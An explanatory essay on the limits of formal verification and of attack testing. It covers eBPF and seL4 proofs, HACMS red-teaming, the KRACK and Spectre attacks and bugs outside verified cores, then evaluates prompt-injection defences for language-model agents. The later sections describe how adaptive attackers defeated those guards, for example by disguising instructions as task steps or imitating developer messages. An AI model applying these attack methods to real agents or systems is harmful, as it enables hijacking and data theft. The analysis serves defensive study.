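Only 30 of the 642 flaws in Chen and colleagues' sample were errors in reasoning about ranges, so even a complete proof of that reasoning would address about 5% of them. But these are among the most dangerous flaws in eBPF, because a wrong range can give an attacker access to any part of the kernel's memory. At the Pwn2Own hacking contest in 2020, a contestant used such a flaw to take full control of a Linux machine.

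Agni's specification has also had gaps. It did not cover speculative execution, in which a processor starts executing a branch before it knows whether the program will take it. As a result, Agni once missed a bug on a branch that no program could take. The researchers have since added an option that covers speculative execution.

Another gap caused trouble for more than three years. Suppose the verifier records r1 both as a range of 0 to 15 and as the bits 1111, which mean exactly 15. The program tests whether r1 is at most 10. The test can never succeed, but an older version of the verifier used only the range, so it analysed the branch where the test succeeds. It narrowed the range to 0–10. The shared routine then raised the lower limit to 15 to match the bits, producing a range from 15 to 10. The verifier detected the impossible range, reset r1 to "any value" and continued.

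This behaviour satisfies the soundness condition. The condition requires the new record to include every value of r1 that passes the test, and no value passes. The behaviour is also harmless at run time, since the program never takes that branch. But it could make the verifier reject a valid program because of code that never runs. In one outage, valid programs from Cilium, a networking tool for large groups of machines, failed to load after a reboot, and an entire cluster lost its connections.

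The remedy is to detect that the two records have no value in common and skip the branch. Comparing their highest and lowest values isn't enough. For example, the pattern x10x, where x is an unknown bit, allows 4, 5, 12 and 13. The range 7 to 9 lies between 4 and 13 but contains none of these values. Vishwanathan and colleagues wrote a function that takes a number and finds the next higher one that fits the pattern. Given 7, it returns 12, which is above 9, so the program can't take the branch. They proved the function correct with Z3 and in Lean, and Linux has adopted it. Their full check, which compares all five of the verifier's records for a register, added about 1.5% overhead on average.

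### What the seL4 proof covers

seL4 is a microkernel, which means that it does only the jobs that a kernel can't leave to other programs, such as dividing up memory and passing messages. Device drivers, file systems and network software run outside it as separate programs. A program can use a region of memory or contact another program only if it holds a capability, a kind of permit that the kernel keeps on its behalf.

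The proof has several layers:

1. The specification describes the effect of every request a program can make. It satisfies two security properties: no program can change data without authority (integrity) or read data without authority (confidentiality).
2. The kernel's C code does what the specification describes. Trustworthy Systems' *The seL4 verification project*, a page from the Australian research group behind seL4, dates this refinement proof to 2009.
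3. On two families of processor, 32-bit Arm and 64-bit RISC-V, the compiled machine code matches the C code, so users don't need to trust the compiler.

Together, these layers mean that if the proof's assumptions hold, an attacker who takes over one program can't alter or read another program's memory, no matter what requests they make the first program send the kernel or in what order. The only exception is if the system's designer gave the first program a capability to do so.

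These proofs do not cover every version of seL4. seL4's *Verified Configurations* lists one 32-bit Arm board with the full set of proofs, while the version for 64-bit PC processors has a proof that the C code meets the specification but no proofs of the security properties. *seL4 security proofs now complete on AArch64* reports that the company Proofcraft has since completed the confidentiality proof for 64-bit Arm. No listed configuration has a proof for the kernel's startup code or for the hardware that controls which memory devices such as network cards can reach. The confidentiality proof also does not cover timing channels. In *What's verified, what's not, and what does it mean?*, Andronick warns users that downloading seL4 does not give them a verified kernel, and that running a verified kernel does not make the rest of their system verified.

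In version 13.0.0, released in July 2024, seL4's developers fixed a flaw in a configuration they had not verified. According to seL4's release history, a program with access to a certain kind of object could crash the kernel on machines with several processor cores and support for virtual machines. The flaw doesn't contradict the proof, but anyone who chose seL4 for its proof and ran it in that configuration was exposed.

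### Attacking a drone and a helicopter

The US defence research agency DARPA tested this kind of design in its High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems (HACMS) programme. Engineers rebuilt the software of a small quadcopter and of Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a full-sized helicopter that can fly itself. A red team of professional penetration testers attacked both aircraft at the start and end of each of three 18-month phases. Fisher writes in *Formal Methods at Scale* that the team had the documentation and source code and took part in design meetings. It therefore knew far more than most attackers would.

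At the start, the Red Team easily took control of both aircraft. Aviation Today's *Rockwell Collins-Led Team Demos Ability to Guard Flight Control Software From Attack* (2017) describes an attack on the drone. The attackers used its Wi-Fi to get into the Linux system that ran the camera. From there, a weakness in the memory protection let them reach the drone's encryption keys. They replaced the keys, which let them fly the drone from their own ground station.

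After the rebuild, the Red Team failed in every test. DARPA says it then made the task easier by giving the team access to the part of the helicopter's software that ran the camera. The team couldn't break out of that part, even when the engineers repeated the test in flight with two pilots on board. Fisher adds that the team could run its own code in that part with full administrator rights. Attackers could still interfere with the drone's camera, but they could no longer reach its flight controls or keys.

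In August 2021, DARPA also let visitors to the hacker conference DEF CON attack the quadcopter. They failed too, according to *seL4 defeats DEF CON hackers*, a post on seL4's own forum.

The exercises can't show that the proof contributed to this success, because the engineers changed several things at once. They separated the camera from the flight software, generated some of the new code from formal specifications, and eventually put seL4 underneath. Trustworthy Systems' *SMACCM* dates the quadcopter's seL4 board to August 2015. Earlier demonstrations used a different operating system, so seL4 can't explain any resistance to attack before then. Nobody gave the Red Team an aircraft with the same separation but an unverified kernel. Separation alone would have blocked the original route from the camera to the keys, unless the attackers had found a flaw in the kernel that enforced it.

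That exception is the reason to want a proof. As James Anderson observed of the tiger teams, a failed attack shows only that one team didn't find a way out, but the proof covers every request the camera's software could have made. The exercises tested the kernel proof's assumption that the engineers had set up the separation correctly and left no route around it.

### How many Linux flaws a microkernel would remove

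Biggs, Lee and Heiser (2018), in *The Jury Is In*, give a rough way to estimate how much security comes from separation and how much from proof. They took 115 critical Linux flaws from the CVE records, excluded three that had too little information to judge, and asked how each of the other 112 would have affected a system built around a microkernel. Their hypothetical application needed a network, storage and a console. If a flaw was in a component the application didn't need, such as a USB driver, an attacker could take over that component without affecting the application.

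Separation alone would have eliminated 33 of the flaws (29%), according to Heiser's 2018 post on the microkerneldude blog, *microkernels really do improve security*. A verified microkernel such as seL4 would have eliminated 40%, or about 45. By this estimate, separation accounts for nearly three-quarters of the eliminated flaws, and the proof for the other dozen or so. The paper also concludes that 96% of the flaws would have fallen below critical severity, a finding quoted in Slashdot's *Linux Study Argues Monolithic OS Design Leads To Critical Exploits*.

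These are judgements about a system that nobody built, and Heiser helps lead the seL4 project. The study also counts only the flaws that a new design would remove, not those in the large amount of new code that separate Linux services would need to communicate. Even so, the estimate fits the HACMS results, in which separation was enough to block the original attack.

### Size, attention and exposure

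The thousands of flaws in eBPF and the few known in seL4 don't by themselves show that proof works far better than testing, partly because Linux is much larger than seL4. Linux had about 26 million lines of code, according to a passage from Biggs and colleagues' paper quoted in *Monolithic OS design is flawed*, which also mentions an optimistic rate of one bug per 2,000 lines. At that rate, Linux would have 13,000 bugs, and a kernel of 10,000 lines, roughly the size of seL4, would have five even without proof.

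Size also matters within eBPF. The runtime contains about 64% of the basic blocks that Chen and colleagues measured in Linux 5.10, and about 74% of the flaws outside the user-space tools. It would have most of the flaws even if its code were no worse than the verifier's. (This is a rough comparison, because the flaws come from many versions of Linux.)

Dasu and colleagues describe the verifier as the eBPF component with the most reported CVEs, yet the runtime has far more entries in Chen and colleagues' dataset. This is probably because security researchers concentrate on the verifier, where one mistake can give an attacker control of the whole kernel, while developers fix runtime faults without announcing them as vulnerabilities. CVE rankings therefore partly reflect where people have looked. Flaws in Linux are also more likely to be found than flaws in seL4, because far more people use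 and attack Linux.

How much a flaw matters depends partly on who can exploit it. Ordinary users can't exploit many of the eBPF flaws because, by default, they can't load programs. A raw count gives these flaws the same weight as one that anyone can trigger by sending a packet.

A fairer test would follow one piece of code over time. Researchers could run one by counting the errors found in the verifier's range calculations before and after Agni's daily checks began. The code would still change between the two periods, but its purpose, users and attackers would stay much the same.

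## How verified systems have failed

A verified system can still fail if its proof rests on a false assumption or its specification omits something its owner needed. Researchers have documented both kinds of failure, most of them outside the part that anyone had proved.

### Unverified code around a verified core

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems that keep copies of data on several servers. Each has a machine-checked proof that its servers follow a protocol for keeping the copies consistent. The proofs assume that some unverified code, which the researchers call the shim layer, sends messages and writes to disk correctly.

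The researchers read the code and specifications, wrote tests, and built a fuzzer that duplicated and reordered network packets and made disk operations fail. When they found a bug in one system, they looked for it in the others. They also looked for bugs that people had reported in unverified systems. In more than eight months they found 16 bugs:

| Location | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Shim layer | 11 | A server erases its old snapshot of the data before it has safely written the new one, so a crash in between loses data |
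| Verification tools | 3 | A build tool reports success although the prover has crashed |
| Specification | 2 | The specification allows a server to carry out the same request twice |

One of the shim bugs, in Verdi, resembles SQL injection. Verdi used spaces and line breaks to separate commands and their arguments, but it didn't escape those characters inside arguments. A client could ask for a key whose name contained a line break followed by a second command, and the server would run both commands. It then sent two replies where the client expected one, so later requests returned the wrong values. Verdi's proof covered how the servers handled commands, but not how they divided the incoming text into commands. Sending the length of each argument before the argument would fix the flaw.

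Fonseca and colleagues searched specifically for protocol bugs in the three verified systems and found none. In a year of bug reports for four unverified systems, they counted 12 protocol bugs, with at least one in every system. They warn against comparing the totals, because the unverified systems are much larger and have far more users. Jones (2017) objected on a mailing list, in *Empirical Study on the Correctness of, Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, that the right comparison is with systems checked by other techniques using the same resources. That is a fair objection to any claim about value for money, but the location of the bugs is still informative. It matches the results for CompCert, where Csmith found bugs only outside the proved parts. IronFleet, which had the least unverified code of the three systems, had no shim bugs.

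### A property that nobody stated

WPA2 protects most Wi-Fi traffic. A laptop and a router exchange four messages, called a handshake, to agree on an encryption key. Researchers published proof sketches for the core of the handshake in 2005, and others proved the encryption secure. But in 2017, Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens broke WPA2 with a key reinstallation attack (KRACK).

After the third message, the laptop installs the key, which means that it starts using it. It also sets a packet counter to zero. The counter matters because the laptop encrypts each packet with both the key and the counter, and must never use the same pair twice. The attack makes it do so:

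1. The attacker, positioned between the two devices, blocks the laptop's fourth message, which confirms that it has installed the key.
2. The laptop starts sending encrypted packets.
3. The router has received no confirmation, so it sends the third message again, and the attacker lets it through.
4. The laptop installs the same key again and resets the counter, so its next packets reuse the earlier pairs.

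The key and counter together determine a string of bits k, which the laptop combines with the packet by exclusive or (written ⊕), an operation that gives 1 where two bits differ and 0 where they match. If two packets p₁ and p₂ use the same k, the attacker intercepts

c₁ = p₁ ⊕ k and c₂ = p₂ ⊕ k.

Combining them cancels k:

c₁ ⊕ c₂ = p₁ ⊕ p₂.

An attacker who knows or can guess p₁ can now calculate p₂. With two of WPA2's three encryption options, the attacker can also forge packets.

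The attacker never learns the key and can't impersonate either device in the handshake, so everything the researchers had proved about the handshake remains true. But their proofs did not model how the key is installed, so they did not require the laptop to install it only once. *Key Reinstallation Attacks* (Vanhoef, 2017) points out that nobody had proved the handshake and encryption secure in combination. Vanhoef found the flaw while rereading an operating system's Wi-Fi code and wondering what would happen if the function that installs the key ran twice.

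The first repairs failed too. Vanhoef and Piessens had argued only informally that their countermeasures would work, and the standards body IEEE adopted slightly different ones. In 2018 the two researchers bypassed both sets. Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger (2020), in *A Formal Analysis of IEEE 802.11's WPA2*, then built the first model detailed enough to represent the attacks. It included repeated messages, key installation and a power-saving mode that one of the later attacks exploits. They also partly dropped the usual assumption of perfect encryption by letting the attacker benefit from a reused counter.

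Without countermeasures, the model reproduced the known attacks. With some of the newer countermeasures, the protocol tool Tamarin proved that the keys stay secret and that the handshake authenticates both devices. The reproduced attacks are a good reason to trust the proof, because they show that the model could have detected a failed repair. The 2005 model had already passed the broken protocol, so it would have passed any repair.

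### A machine model without memory limits or time

Another Verdi bug was in code generated from a verified function that listed the requests a lagging server had missed. The function called itself once for each entry, and when a server was more than 500,000 requests behind, the function ran out of memory and crashed. The proof did not cover the function's memory use.

Spectre, a family of attacks that became public in January 2018, exploits a larger omission. Suppose a trusted program contains these lines, and an attacker chooses `i`:

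```
if i < length:
    y = table[data[i]]
```

The check should stop the attacker from reading past the end of `data`. But a modern processor predicts the outcome of the check and starts on the second line early. If `i` is too large, `data[i]` may be a secret stored elsewhere in memory, and its value determines which part of `table` the processor reads. When the check fails, the processor discards the result, so the program never receives `y`. However, the part of `table` that the processor read is still in the cache, a small store of recently used data. By timing later reads, the attacker can find out which part is fast to read and work out the secret from that.

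seL4's confidentiality proof did not exclude this, because its model has no concept of time, as Heiser, Klein and Murray (2019), in *Can We Prove Time Protection?*, acknowledge. Asked about such flaws on the seL4 mailing list (2020), Heiser replied that "verification has to assume sane behaviour of the hardware". seL4's developers had known about the gap. According to CSIRO's *Crisis*, an article from Australia's national research agency, they warned in September 2017 that nobody could write an operating system free of timing leaks until manufacturers specified how their processors behave over time.

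*Time Protection* (2018) proposed time protection as a remedy for timing leaks and implemented it in an experimental version of seL4. The kernel groups programs into security domains and prevents domains from sharing any hardware whose state affects speed. It divides the large caches between domains, and resets smaller caches and other state inside the processor core whenever it switches domains. A reset takes longer if the previous domain has left more unsaved data. To prevent this difference from leaking information, the kernel always waits for a fixed time before starting the next domain.

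One might expect a proof about timing to require the exact duration of every instruction, which manufacturers don't publish. Heiser and colleagues avoid this problem. They treat the duration as

t = f(s),

where s is the state of the hardware that the instruction depends on, and f is some fixed but unknown function. If another domain can't affect s, it can't affect t either, whatever f is. The proof therefore has to show only which domains can affect which state, and seL4's developers already had methods for that.

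Proving that a kernel prevents timing leaks has taken years. In *Proving the Absence of Microarchitectural Timing Channels*, Buckley, Sison and colleagues (2023) proved that time protection holds if the kernel touches only memory in the right partition and the hardware meets a list of requirements. The proof covers a single processor core and domains that don't communicate. While writing it, they discovered that one of the original countermeasures was unsound. The kernel had loaded some shared data into the cache at every switch to put the cache into a known state, but ordinary reads can't guarantee this unless the kernel's designers know how the processor decides what to discard. Buckley and colleagues also measured a leak of 9.6 millibits between domains that shared a copy of the kernel. With separate copies, it fell to 0.1 millibits, no more than sampling error would produce.

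The proof for the real kernel is unfinished. In a 2025 thesis, Liang used a small part of the kernel to demonstrate a method for extending the proof to the C code. In *Where are we with Time Protection?*, Sison (2026) describes new ways for domains to send one-way messages without a timing leak, but these have not yet been verified. Time protection also needs hardware support, and the mainstream x86 and Arm processors that researchers tested had state that no instruction could reset. In *fence.t.s*, Wistoff, Heiser and Benini (2024) closed the leaks in an advanced open-source processor design, which reduced performance by 1.0%.

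A more detailed model can also expose timing flaws before manufacture. CHERI is a hardware extension that restricts which memory a program can reach. Earlier proofs about it used a description of its instructions that left out timing. *VeriCHERI* (2024) instead checked the circuit design, which specifies what happens in each clock cycle, and found a potential timing attack similar to Meltdown, which is closely related to Spectre.

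### A specification that permits harm

A program can meet its specification exactly and still do something its owner would forbid. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (Philipp, 2026) describes a recent example from a project in which AI agents wrote all the code and proofs. The agents built checkers that, like Keel, verify certificates that a formula has no solution, and proved that these checkers never accept a false certificate. A human reviewed the specifications, but no human read the code or the proofs.

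Philipp then planted defects to see which the project's automatic safeguards would stop. The verified checkers rejected all five false certificates, and a tool that checks the translation of programs into formulas withstood all 39 attacks. But the ordinary software that enforced the project's rules let through 14 of 17 defects, which included an edit to an approved specification and a test that could never fail. After repairs, it stopped all 17, though Philipp had designed the repairs around those same defects.

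The automatic safeguards could not have stopped a hidden behaviour that the specification allows. The theorem restricts what a checker may accept, but it doesn't require the checker to accept every valid certificate, and it doesn't limit what else the program does. A dishonest programmer could exploit either omission in a program that still passes every proof. Philipp argued this from the wording of the theorem and did not build such a checker. The case therefore shows that the gap exists, but it isn't evidence that an agent is likely to use it.

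### Errors in the tools that check proofs

A proof is also unreliable if the tool that checked it was wrong. IronFleet's build tool read the verifier's report only as far as the line with the error count, so it missed a later line reporting that the prover had crashed. It could therefore approve any program, even one containing a false assertion. The prover did crash, because its package included incompatible files.

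In 2026, Philipp's project found similar faults in three proof checkers and five solvers. One checker, drat-trim, treated a number with a leading zero as octal (base 8), so it read −010 as −8. Suppose a formula requires only that x₈ is true and x₁₀ is false, so it has a solution. If the file writes the second condition as −010, drat-trim reads it as "x₈ is false", finds a contradiction, and accepts a one-line proof that the formula has no solution.

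Other errors were in the reasoning itself. The solver Z3, on which many of the tools in earlier sections rely, wrongly reported that no set B satisfies these conditions:

B ⊆ {0, 1, 2, 3}, 0 ∈ B, and |B ∪ B| = 4.

A new solver called Sundance produced a valid proof of the wrong problem because it ignored commands that withdraw earlier conditions. Philipp also lists three known bugs in Verus, a verifier for Rust programs, each of which lets a false statement pass as proved.

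These faults are serious for anyone who relies on a single tool, but none shows that an attacker has broken a verified product. The Z3 error affects a feature that Verus doesn't use, and the project's own verified checkers rejected every false certificate. The maintainers of Z3 and of another solver, clasp, responded to the reports within three days.

### Testing a specification

Engineers can look for gaps in a specification by breaking the program and checking whether the proof still passes. Fonseca and colleagues did this to IronFleet. They changed seven lines to turn off its protection against duplicate requests, and the proof still passed. IronFleet's developers replied that they had never meant the specification to cover duplicates, so a user who relied on the proof for that protection would have been mistaken.

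The researchers also built a tool that finds such changes by disabling code at random. The average number of attempts it needed ranged from 18 to 8,015, depending on which function they chose for it to alter, so the method can be slow without guidance on which function to target.

In Philipp's project, 492 altered versions of the verified code compiled, and the proofs rejected 396 of them, or 80%. Many of the other 96 were harmless, but some changed the verdict that a checker printed, so it could reject a certificate but still report success. The agents extended the proof to cover the printing of the verdict, and it then caught all 23 alterations of that kind.

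Another method is to derive consequences from the specification and check whether they are acceptable. Fonseca and colleagues combined IronFleet's specification with that of a simple counter, and proved that a single request to the counter could leave it at any value. Few people would notice this from reading the specification, but once it is stated, anyone can tell that it is wrong. Philipp's agents tested one of their specifications on 958 small logic programs, and the results all matched those of an established solver. Such a comparison can reveal a mistake in the specification, but not one that the solver shares.

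The natural remedy for the gap Philipp identified is to prove completeness as well as soundness, so that the checker must accept every valid certificate. Soundness alone permits needless refusals, like those behind the Cilium outage. Completeness would rule out selective refusals, but a separate rule is needed to stop a program from secretly copying its input elsewhere. There is little evidence yet on how well this works in practice. Philipp recommends proving completeness but did not make it a goal of the project, and it is a demanding requirement for a checker that deliberately supports only some kinds of certificate.

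The evidence for independent review is stronger. One of the project's specifications, which defined the meaning of the verifier's intermediate language, failed four of its six reviews, while the automatic validator reported complete success every time. In the fourth review, the reviewer built a working exploit that got a false statement both validated and certified because two programs divided the same text into symbols differently. The reviewers were AI agents that worked separately from the authors, but nearly all of them used the same model, so they may have missed the same errors. These results show that review finds errors that automatic checks miss, but the number of errors the reviewers missed is unknown.

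### Does proof only move the risk?

A sceptic might conclude that proof only moves the risk from the code to the specification. Philipp partly agrees, writing that zero trust "moves trust; it does not remove it".

Fonseca and colleagues point out that a single coding mistake is enough to cause a failure in ordinary software, whereas in verified code the specification or the verifier must also have a matching error. IronFleet's specification allowed duplicate requests, but this caused no failure because its code blocked them. All 16 bugs in the three systems arose in the specification, shim layer or auxiliary tools. These parts typically came to a few hundred lines, small enough to examine, and tests aimed at them detected 13 of the bugs. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists the proofs' assumptions and warns, for example, that drivers for devices with direct access to memory need their own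 verification.

This reply is strongest for assumptions that somebody has written down. The standard that contains WPA2 runs to more than 3,000 pages, and the proof's omission of key installation went unnoticed from 2005 to 2017. The trusted base is also not always small. Verus's front end, for example, is a large program that keeps changing. But doing without the WPA2 proof would not have helped, because testers who never thought of installing a key twice would not have tested for it. The proof did harm only to the extent that it discouraged people from looking further.

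## Attack experiments on guards that rely on a language model

The WPA2 proofs left something out, but the researchers could specify exactly what the protocol should do. Nobody has an exact definition of what it means for a language model to use the information in a stranger's email while ignoring the stranger's instructions. The makers of most defences against prompt injection therefore have no exact property to prove. Instead, they attack the defence and measure how often the attacks succeed, a rate that depends heavily on how hard the attacker tries.

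### How a model can be made to resist

The easiest defence is a better prompt. A developer can warn the model not to obey outside text, put delimiters around part of the text, or repeat the user's request after the outside text so that the model reads it last. Another defence is to train the model on known attacks, in the hope that it will learn to resist new ones. A third is to add a classifier, usually a smaller model, that screens the main model's inputs or outputs and blocks anything that looks like an injection.

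Some defences use a hidden test. Data Sentinel prompts a model to repeat a secret word while ignoring the suspect text. If the model fails to repeat the word, it has probably followed instructions in the text. MELON runs the agent twice, the second time replacing the user's request with a harmless request for a summary. A tool call that appears in both runs probably came from the outside text, because the user's request was missing from the second run.

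All these defences rely on a model to judge text correctly, and the attacker writes the text.

### AgentDojo

Most researchers test such defences on a shared benchmark. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, built four simulated settings for an agent: an office with email, a calendar and files; the messaging service Slack; a travel agency; and a bank. The first version had 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 attacker's goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account. Pairing every task with every goal in the same setting gives

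40×6 + 21×5 + 20×7 + 16×9 = 629

test cases, where the products are for the office, Slack, travel and the bank. By 2026 the benchmark had more than 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

In each case, the benchmark places the attacker's text where an outsider could plausibly write it and the agent will read it during the user's task, such as in the body of an email. When the agent has finished, ordinary code inspects the simulated setting, for example to check whether money has left the account. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might fool the judge too. They measured how many tasks the agent completes with and without an attack, and how often the attacker achieves their goal.

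In 2024, the models completed fewer than 66% of the tasks even when nobody attacked them. Attacks succeeded against the best agents in under 25% of cases, and adding a separate detector reduced the success rate to 8%. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, probably because weaker ones often failed to carry out the attacker's task even after accepting it.

These attacks were fixed in advance. The main one was a template instruction to do another task before the user's. Debenedetti and colleagues warned that it is very easy to build a defence that stops any particular attack, and they designed AgentDojo so that researchers could add attacks aimed at each new defence. Many developers of defences ran only the attacks that came with it.

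### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues retested 12 published defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. Ten were meant to stop prompt injection or something close to it, and the other two to stop jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get forbidden material out of a model.

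The researchers used four kinds of attacker. Each proposes an attack, observes how close it came to working, keeps the most promising attempts and revises them:

- A gradient attack uses the model's internal calculations to find changes of wording that make the desired output more likely.
- A reinforcement-learning attack trains a second language model to write attacks, rewarding it when they come close.
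- A search attack keeps a pool of past attempts, and a language model rewrites the better ones.
- More than 500 people took part in an online contest with $20,000 in prizes.

On AgentDojo, the fixed attack succeeded as little as 1% of the time against two prompting defences, delimiters and repeating the user's request. The search attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both. Against MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, the success rate rose from 2% with the fixed attack to 96% with the search attack. Two other defences based on training failed in every case tested. Three of the four classifiers let through more than 90% of the attacks, and the fourth, PIGuard, let through 71%.

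Guards that use hidden test questions did little better. Against Data Sentinel, the attacker made the model do a different task from the one assigned, with over 80% accuracy, and the model still passed the secret-word test. The search attack succeeded against MELON 76% of the time when the attacker didn't know how MELON worked, and 95% of the time when the attacker had a description of it.

The successful attacks used familiar tricks, and Nasr and colleagues noticed no completely new strategy. Some attacks presented the attacker's task as a step that the user's own task required. Others imitated messages from the system's developer. Against classifiers, the attacker disguised the instruction as a dull office procedure so that it would not look hostile. Against MELON, the attacker's text contained a condition so that the agent would obey it in the first run and ignore it in the run that asked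 for a summary. Against Data Sentinel, the text redefined the terms of the assigned task. Some jailbreaks presented requests as fiction. The search also tried codes, foreign languages and unusual formats.

### What a 95% success rate means

These percentages don't mean that 95 of every 100 malicious emails would work. The search attack had up to 800 tries at each case, and the researchers counted the case as a success if any of them worked. The results for two models show what the defences contributed:

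| Defence | Fixed attack, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Search attack, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Search attack, GPT-5 Mini | Ordinary tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 75% | 74% |
| Delimiters | 28% | 99% | 47% | 75% |
| Repeated request | 21% | 95% | 69% | 73% |
| PromptGuard (classifier) | 26% | 94% | 75% | 72% |
| Model Armor (classifier) | 28% | 90% | 56% | 59% |
| PIGuard (classifier) | 0% | 71% | 49% | 39% |
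| MELON | 0% | 89% | 71% | 58% |

The fixed attack never worked on GPT-5 Mini with no defence in place, so even a useless defence would have scored perfectly against it on that model. The 1% figure for delimiters has a similar weakness, because it comes from adding them to MetaSecAlign, on which the fixed attack succeeded only 5% of the time without them.

Nasr and colleagues conclude that the prompting defences made the models no more robust. This is right for Gemini, but on GPT-5 Mini delimiters reduced the search attack's success rate from 75% to 47%. The researchers expected a larger attack budget to break GPT-5 Mini too, which is plausible but untested. Some defences also slowed the attacker. In successful attacks on Gemini, the median number of tries rose from 13 with no defence to 46 with PIGuard. But PIGuard also reduced the agent's completion rate on ordinary tasks by almost half.

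The human contestants did better than the search. The search succeeded in 69% of the 29 scenarios that both attempted, while in each one at least one person succeeded. This is partly because there were many contestants, since the best individual to attempt all 29 succeeded in 75%. Most submissions failed, and fewer than 1% worked when GPT-5 Mini had delimiters, though at least one person still succeeded.

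The experiments gave the attacker more feedback than a real attacker may get. The search attack could read the agent's responses and, for classifiers, their confidence scores, whereas someone who emails a stranger's agent may never learn whether the message worked. But an attacker can often buy the same product, practise on it in private, and then send only the version that works.

Classifiers and trained models learn from past attacks. A fixed test also draws on past attacks, so it mostly measures resistance to the attacks the defence was built for.

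### A filter that leaked nothing

Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, tested a simpler task over a longer period. They put three secrets, such as an access code, into a model's instructions. An attacker, also driven by a language model, tried to extract them through chat. It sent ten attacks per round for up to 500 rounds, and chose among more than 40 strategies based on how the target model had responded. The researchers ran more than 20,000 attacks on nine configurations in all.

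They scored each response with fixed rules. A secret was worth 0.30, the name of the chatbot's persona 0.10, and each run of at least seven words copied from the instructions 0.05. A score of 0.9, the equivalent of all three secrets, counted as critical. The individual defences that depended on a model reached that level as follows:

| Defence | Round of the first critical leak |
|---|---|
| Screening the user's messages with patterns and a classifier | 39 |
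| Rules against revealing secrets | 49 |
| Delimiters around the user's message | 84 |
| Telling the model that its instructions outrank the user's | 247 |
| Security rules at both the start and end of the prompt | 277 |

The order of the defences may partly reflect luck, because each figure comes from one run. The timing of the breakthroughs is more informative, as they came suddenly after many rounds of almost no progress. The defence in the last row leaked nothing worse than a phrase from its instructions in its first 25 rounds, so a tester who stopped there would have thought it nearly perfect.

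The defence that held was an output filter, ordinary code that blocks any response containing text from the model's instructions. Deep and colleagues attacked it, alone and combined with the other defences, and report no leaks in 15,000 attacks, although the six runs of 5,000 they describe would make 30,000. By the rule of three, 15,000 attacks without a leak put the failure rate below 3/15,000, or 0.02%, with 95% confidence.

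That bound fails if an attacker asks for the secret in another form. If the secret is K7Q2, the filter blocks "K7Q2" but not "K-7-Q-2", a reversed spelling or a translation into code. The test could not detect such leaks because its scoring also matched only exact text. The filter was built to block almost everything the test would have counted as a leak, so a score of zero was close to inevitable. Deep and colleagues acknowledge that encoded or reworded secrets would escape both checks. The attempts also weren't independent random draws, since the attacker based each round on earlier ones.

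The filter still has an advantage that no prompt has. Its rule, "no response contains this exact text", is precise enough for a programmer to verify by reading the code, and no clever argument from the attacker can change its verdict. The experiment adds little to that guarantee, and it doesn't show that the rule is the right one. A safer design is to keep the secret out of the prompt altogether, as Deep and colleagues also recommend. (Several of them work for Swept AI, which sells security tests for AI systems.)

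Their statement that every defence relying on the model eventually broke is also slightly too strong. With all the defences except the output filter in place, 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked something, but no score exceeded 0.10. A single secret would have scored 0.30, so no secret leaked in a form the test could detect. Combining weak defences therefore helped considerably, at least for 500 rounds.

### Why a hundred attempts succeed less often than expected

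Some developers now publish how attack success rates grow with repeated attempts. Gray Swan, a security firm, tested Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic released in November 2025. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Rival models had rates as high as 92%. Anthropic explains in the system card, its report on the model's tests, that Gray Swan took the attacks from a contest among expert testers and chose ones that had worked on several models. These attacks are much stronger than those on an average malicious web page.

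If every attempt had the same independent 4.7% chance, the expected rates would be

1 − 0.953^10 ≈ 38% and 1 − 0.953^100 ≈ 99%.

The observed rates are lower because the attempts are not alike. Suppose that 63% of the attacker's targets are vulnerable, with a 7.5% chance of success at each attempt, and that the others never fall. The expected rates are then:

| Attempts | Calculation | Expected | Observed |
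|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.63 × 0.075 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 0.63 × (1 − 0.925^10) | 34% | 33.6% |
| 100 | 0.63 × (1 − 0.925^100) | 63% | 63.0% |

The good fit doesn't prove that the other 37% are immune. A target with a 1-in-10,000 chance per attempt would look the same after a hundred tries, and a cleverer attack might succeed at once. The average can also mislead, because in the model an agent in the vulnerable group faces about a 54% risk from ten attempts, compared with 34% across all agents.

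Anthropic also used Shade, a Gray Swan tool that revises its attacks between attempts. When Opus 4.5 was writing code and could reason at length before acting, Shade's success rate rose from 0.3% with one attempt to 10.0% with 200. For the earlier Claude Sonnet 4.5, it rose from 17.7% to 70.0%. When Opus 4.5 operated a computer through its screen, also with time to reason, none of the attacks worked. Anthropic said it would develop stronger attacks in response.

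In February 2026 VentureBeat reported the corresponding figures for the next model, Claude Opus 4.6. It resisted every attack in a coding test, but when it operated a computer, 17.8% of attacks succeeded on the first attempt and 78.6% by the 200th. Anthropic's additional safeguards reduced the latter figure to 57.1%. The newer model may have been worse at this task, or the attacks may have improved. If the attacks improved, the previous model's zero mostly reflected the weakness of the old attacks.

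The computer-use tests were probably small as well. Their published success rates at 200 attempts are all multiples of one-fourteenth, which suggests about 14 scenarios. With Sonnet 4.5, the safeguards appeared to raise the attacker's success rate from 85.7% to 92.9%, but if there were 14 scenarios, that is a difference of only one scenario.

### What newer models have improved

Models have become much harder to hijack since then. Gray Swan, Anthropic and the British and American government AI institutes developed a new benchmark with 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks, according to the Japanese technology site TechFeed. It replaced the benchmark used for Opus 4.5, on which Claude models had scored almost perfectly. On the new benchmark, attacks on Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026, succeeded 0.2% of the time when the attacker had one attempt and 2.0% with 15. For its predecessor, Opus 4.8,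 the figures were 0.5% and 5.5%.

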